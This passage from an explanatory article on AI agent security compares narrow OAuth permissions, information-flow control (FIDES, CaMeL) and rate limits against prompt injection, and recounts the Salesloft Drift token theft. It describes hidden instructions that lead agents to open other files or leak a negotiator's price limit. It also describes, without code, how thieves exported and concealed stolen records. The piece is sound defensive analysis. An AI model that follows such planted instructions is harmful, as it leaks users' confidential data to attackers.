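| Gemma 3 4B | 1,280 | 636 | 454 (35.5%) | 0 |
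| Llama 3.1 8B | 1,280 | 522 | 484 (37.8%) | 0 |
| Llama 3.2 3B | 1,267 | 629 | 465 (36.7%) | 0 |
| Mistral 7B | 1,277 | 154 | 133 (10.4%) | 0 |
| Qwen3 4B | 1,270 | 113 | 113 (8.9%) | 0 |

In total, the models made 2,054 choices outside their permissions, and 1,649 of them succeeded with the broad token. The other 405 failed even with the broad token. In one case, the model asked for a calendar called "project-1", which didn't exist. The narrow permissions refused those 405 requests too, but that prevented no harm.

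The zero only confirms that the checks worked, so Hagverdiyev doesn't present it as a discovery. The results for the broad token are more informative because they show how often a misled model's request would have gone through.

The experiment also can't show how much Maya would gain from the scopes platforms offer today, because Hagverdiyev didn't test a permission that limited only the action. In one scenario, the task was to summarise `inventory.csv`, and a hidden instruction made the model open `payroll.csv` instead. A general permission to read files would have allowed that. The narrow permissions stopped it because they specified the file as well as the action. Gmail's scopes limit the action but not which messages it applies to.

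He also supplied the permissions himself, from a reviewed list for each scenario. None of the 2,463 permitted requests from the attacked runs was refused, but a list written by Maya or a model would wrongly allow some requests and wrongly refuse others.

### What did the narrow permissions cost?

After a refusal, the models continued safely in 54% to 100% of cases, depending on the model and the kind of permission. Mistral did worst and Qwen3 did best. "Safely" here includes doing nothing further, and Hagverdiyev didn't check whether the model's final answer was correct. The results therefore don't show how much useful work an agent loses when a server refuses one of its requests.

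The delay was small. A request took a median of about two milliseconds with the broad token or the ordinary narrow one, and 14 to 24 milliseconds with Open Policy Agent. Requests with DPoP were slightly faster than the rest, at 1.3 to 1.8 milliseconds. The server checked the scope before the signature, so it could refuse many of these requests early, and their speed doesn't show that checking a signature saves time. All the tests ran on one computer, and a company's gateway would add network delays.

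Hagverdiyev also tried part of AgentDojo, the benchmark that PAuth's designers adapted. He used three banking tasks and three calendar tasks with one model, Llama 3.2 3B. Attacks succeeded in 11 of 24 runs with the broad token and in none of 24 with the narrow one. But the agent completed its task in only five of the 24 attacked runs with the broad token and six with the narrow one. Without an attack, it completed nine of 24 with each. In several runs it never reached the hidden instruction, and a third of all the runs ended because the model wrote an invalid request, so some attacks may have failed because the agent didn't get far enough to do damage, regardless of its permissions.

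The models in these tests are much smaller than those behind most commercial agents. Hagverdiyev also ran the main scenarios on two larger models, OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Luna and Meta's Muse Spark 1.3. Luna made 253 valid decisions and Muse Spark made 234. Neither model chose an action outside its permissions, so the permissions had no effect. This suggests that larger models resist simple hidden instructions fairly well. But the attacks used fixed, simple wording, and a real attacker can keep rewriting an instruction until one version works.

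The evidence on limiting actions alone is better. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) tested a defence called Tool Filter, in which, before the agent starts, a model removes the tools that the task doesn't need. On AgentDojo, with OpenAI's GPT-4o, it cut successful attacks by 87%, from 152 to 20. The other 20 used tools that the filter had left in place.

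### What passes every check?

Maya's rules let the agent read four fields of Acme's record. Suppose she also lets it read the internal notes, because they show what Ortiz has already been promised. The notes also record that Maya would accept a 15% discount. On Thursday, Ortiz forwards a colleague's question that contains a hidden instruction for the agent to include the notes in its reply.

If the model complies, it reads a permitted field of a permitted record and sends the text to a permitted person, without an attachment and before Friday. The gateway allows every step, and Acme learns Maya's price limit.

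PAuth's test didn't include this kind of attack. Hagverdiyev says that a list of actions and resources can't detect data leaking through an allowed action.

It can't detect repetition either. In one of Hagverdiyev's early trials, an agent made a legitimate payment twice. The permission covered that payment but didn't limit how many times the agent could make it. A limit on the number of payments would probably have stopped the second one. He later tested such a limit, but no agent reached it, so he couldn't measure how much it helps.

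If the agent can manage without the notes, Maya's best option is to take them away again. If it can't, she needs a rule about where their contents may go after the agent has read them.

### How does information-flow control work?

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and keeps them attached as the data moves. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, an agent system that uses one label to record whether the data came from a trusted source and another to list who may read it.

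When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result gets the stricter label. Suppose Maya and her manager may read the notes, while Maya, her manager and Ortiz may read the renewal price. Only Maya and her manager may then read a reply that draws on both. Kolhe uses the same intersection for shared channels, but here it also works for people outside the company, as long as someone has added them to the list of readers.

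FIDES checks two rules before the agent uses a tool:

- The agent may send data only to people who are allowed to read it.
- The agent may take an action with real consequences only if no untrusted text influenced the choice.

The rule about readers stops the leak of Maya's notes, because Ortiz isn't on the list of people allowed to read them. The hidden instruction can still mislead the model, but the rule limits what the attacker can get. The rule about untrusted text is much stricter. Once an ordinary agent has read Ortiz's email, it can't send anything, because her text is now part of everything the model considers. Maya's agent therefore couldn't answer Acme's questions after reading them.

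FIDES avoids this by hiding the email from the model that makes the decisions. For one of Ortiz's questions, it could work like this:

1. The agent fetches the email. The software stores the text under a name such as `email_1` and shows the main model only that name.
2. The main model asks a second model, which has no tools, to read `email_1` and pick from a fixed list: renewal date, renewal price, contract length or something else.
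3. The main model sees which item the second model picked, looks up that field and replies to Ortiz.

A hidden instruction might make the second model pick the wrong item, so Ortiz would get the contract length when she wanted the price. But a choice from a short list is too small to carry a new instruction to the main model. Maya's company would still have to decide whether to accept this small influence. Costa and colleagues left the fixed lists out of their tests because most of the benchmark's tasks didn't need them.

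The second model can also write longer text, such as a summary, which the main model passes on without seeing. The attacker can then corrupt the summary but can't change who receives it.

### What does this protection cost?

With both kinds of rule in force, no attack in AgentDojo succeeded. The benchmark's automatic scoring still counted three successes against FIDES, but Costa and colleagues inspected them and found no real ones. The price was a large drop in the number of tasks the agent could finish. These are the completion rates with GPT-4o when nobody was attacking:

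| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Adding the checks to an ordinary agent lowers the simple average of the four columns from 84% to 42%, and FIDES raises it only to 50%. FIDES did worse than the ordinary agent on travel, where the rules allowed most of the tools anyway and GPT-4o struggled to work with hidden text.

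Some of this loss comes from the model. With OpenAI's o1, which was better at reasoning, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%. Both models date from 2024, and newer ones would probably do better. But a better model can't recover all of the loss, because many of the banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which is what FIDES is supposed to prevent.

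The perfect security score is also partly due to the test's design. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, so the checks covered every place an attack could come from. A company has to work out for itself which fields are untrusted. If Maya's administrator marks the CRM notes as trusted, and the CRM copies text from customers' emails into them, a hidden instruction in an email could be labeled as trusted.

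FIDES doesn't stop information from leaking through the agent's behaviour. Suppose the agent checks the notes whenever Ortiz proposes a discount, replies at once if Maya would accept it, and otherwise leaves the question for Maya. Ortiz could work out Maya's limit by proposing different figures and timing the answers, even though no reply quotes the notes. Costa and colleagues considered a rule that would prevent this, but it would also stop the agent from doing almost anything visible after reading confidential data.

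The agent's reply of "Yes, that's fine" to Ortiz's request for 10% off could get through here too. FIDES could require that the text of every email come from trusted sources, but then the agent couldn't send a summary of anything a customer wrote.

CaMeL, a system by Debenedetti and colleagues, also uses two models. The main one writes a plan from the user's request alone, and the other reads untrusted data but has no tools. A separate program carries out the plan, tracks where each value came from and applies rules before each tool call. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo while completing a comparable number of tasks. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that the plans are hard to analyse before they run because they are written in a restricted form of Python, and recommends a simpler language.

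Sharma and colleagues say that a company could run either CaMeL or FIDES alongside PAuth. The combination makes sense for Maya because her task rules would limit what the agent can read and whom it can write to, and the labels would limit which of that information it can put in an email. Microsoft has since released FIDES as part of its Agent Framework, a kit for building agents. Developers can now use it without starting from the research code, but someone still has to decide who may read each field.

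### The theft of Salesloft Drift's tokens

In August 2025, thieves used stolen OAuth tokens to copy customer records from hundreds of companies' Salesforce systems. The tokens belonged to Drift, an AI agent from the software company Salesloft that chats with visitors to a company's website. The thieves used Drift's credentials directly, without having to mislead its model, so the case shows what a thief can do with an agent's permissions.

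Infosecurity Magazine's *Salesloft* reports Salesloft's explanation of the attack. Between March and June, the attackers got into Salesloft's GitHub account, where it kept its program code. They then entered Drift's cloud systems and took the tokens that connected Drift to its customers' other software. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 organisations that might be affected.

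Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift*, date the copying from 8 August to at least 18 August. They believe the thieves mainly wanted more credentials, because the thieves searched the stolen records for passwords and cloud access keys. Salesloft and Salesforce cancelled all of Drift's tokens on 20 August.

One of the victims, the internet company Cloudflare (2025), published a detailed timeline. The thieves first entered its Salesforce system on the evening of 12 August. They spent part of the next few days counting records and checking how many requests Salesforce would accept. On 17 August they copied the text of Cloudflare's support cases in three minutes and 22 seconds, then deleted the record of the export job. Customers had pasted secrets into some of those cases, and Cloudflare found 104 of its own access tokens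 in the stolen text. It replaced all of them and saw no sign of misuse.

Here is how the limits discussed so far might have changed the theft from Cloudflare:

| Limit on Drift's access | Likely effect |
|---|---|
| Requests only from Drift's own IP addresses | Blocks the thieves, unless they work from Drift's servers |
| Token tied to a key | Blocks the thieves, unless they steal the key too |
| Access tokens that last five minutes | Little, because the export took less than four minutes and the thieves also had refresh tokens |
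| Only support cases that Drift created | Protects all the other cases |
| Only cases from the past 30 days | Protects older cases |
| At most 100 records an hour | Slows the theft: 10,000 cases would take more than four days |
| Access ends with the task | None, because a website's chat agent works all year |

The incident itself provides evidence only for the limit on IP addresses. The thieves tried one of the stolen tokens on the Salesforce system of Okta, the identity company behind Cross App Access. Okta's *The Salesloft incident* (2025) says the attempt failed because the request came from an IP address that wasn't on Okta's list of allowed addresses. According to CyberScoop, many companies don't use such lists because someone has to set them up by hand, with help from every supplier involved. Okta says the same set of controls, described in its *First Drift, now Gainsight* (2025),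 protected it again that November, when attackers compromised another supplier, Gainsight.

Okta also recommends DPoP, which its paid products support. But these thieves had entered the systems where Drift kept its tokens, and if DPoP's private keys had been stored there too, the thieves could have taken both. To prevent that, Drift would have needed to keep the keys in separate hardware or a separate service.

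Limits on addresses and keys wouldn't have helped if Drift's own agent had followed a hidden instruction from a website visitor. A limit on which records Drift could read works in both situations. Cloudflare used Drift to let visitors contact the company. If that didn't require reading every support case in Salesforce, an administrator could have kept cases private by default and let Drift's user account see only its own. Cloudflare now advises companies to give outside applications the minimum access they need.

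The limit on records per hour would also have slowed the theft. If Cloudflare had a large number of cases, thieves limited to 100 an hour would probably still have been copying them when Salesloft cancelled the tokens. The limit would need to cover bulk exports as well as ordinary requests, since the thieves used Salesforce's bulk interface.

Larsen and colleagues found that on 9 August the thieves also used tokens from Drift's email connection to read mail in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. The thieves couldn't reach other accounts at the same companies, because each token covered only an account that someone had connected to Drift.

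### Mistakes without an attacker

An agent can also do damage without being misled. In Hagverdiyev's experiment, Llama 3.2 twice used the broad token to carry out a harmful action without having read a hidden instruction. One action happened before the model reached the instruction, and the other happened in one of the 800 control runs, which contained no hidden instruction. Both actions were outside the task's permissions, so a narrow token wouldn't have allowed them.

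A mistake inside the task is harder to contain. Suppose Maya asks her agent to delete old newsletters from her mailbox, and it mistakes her correspondence with Acme for newsletters and starts deleting that too. She can't withhold permission to delete, because the task requires it. Information-flow control doesn't help either, since no data leaves the mailbox and the agent can make this mistake without any influence from untrusted text.

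With the Gmail scope `gmail.modify`, the agent can move the Acme messages to the trash, where Maya can recover them, but only the `mail.google.com` scope lets it delete them permanently.

A gateway could add a list of the newsletters' addresses and refuse to delete messages from any other sender. If Maya doesn't want to write the list, the gateway could let the agent delete 50 messages and then hold further deletions until she has looked at those 50. An agent that deletes ten messages a second would reach that limit in five seconds, but she would have at most 50 messages to check.

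Maya might instead tell the agent, in the conversation, to ask before it deletes anything, but the model then has to remember the instruction and apply it to every message. If it forgets the instruction after the first few hundred messages, the mail server will still accept the next deletion.
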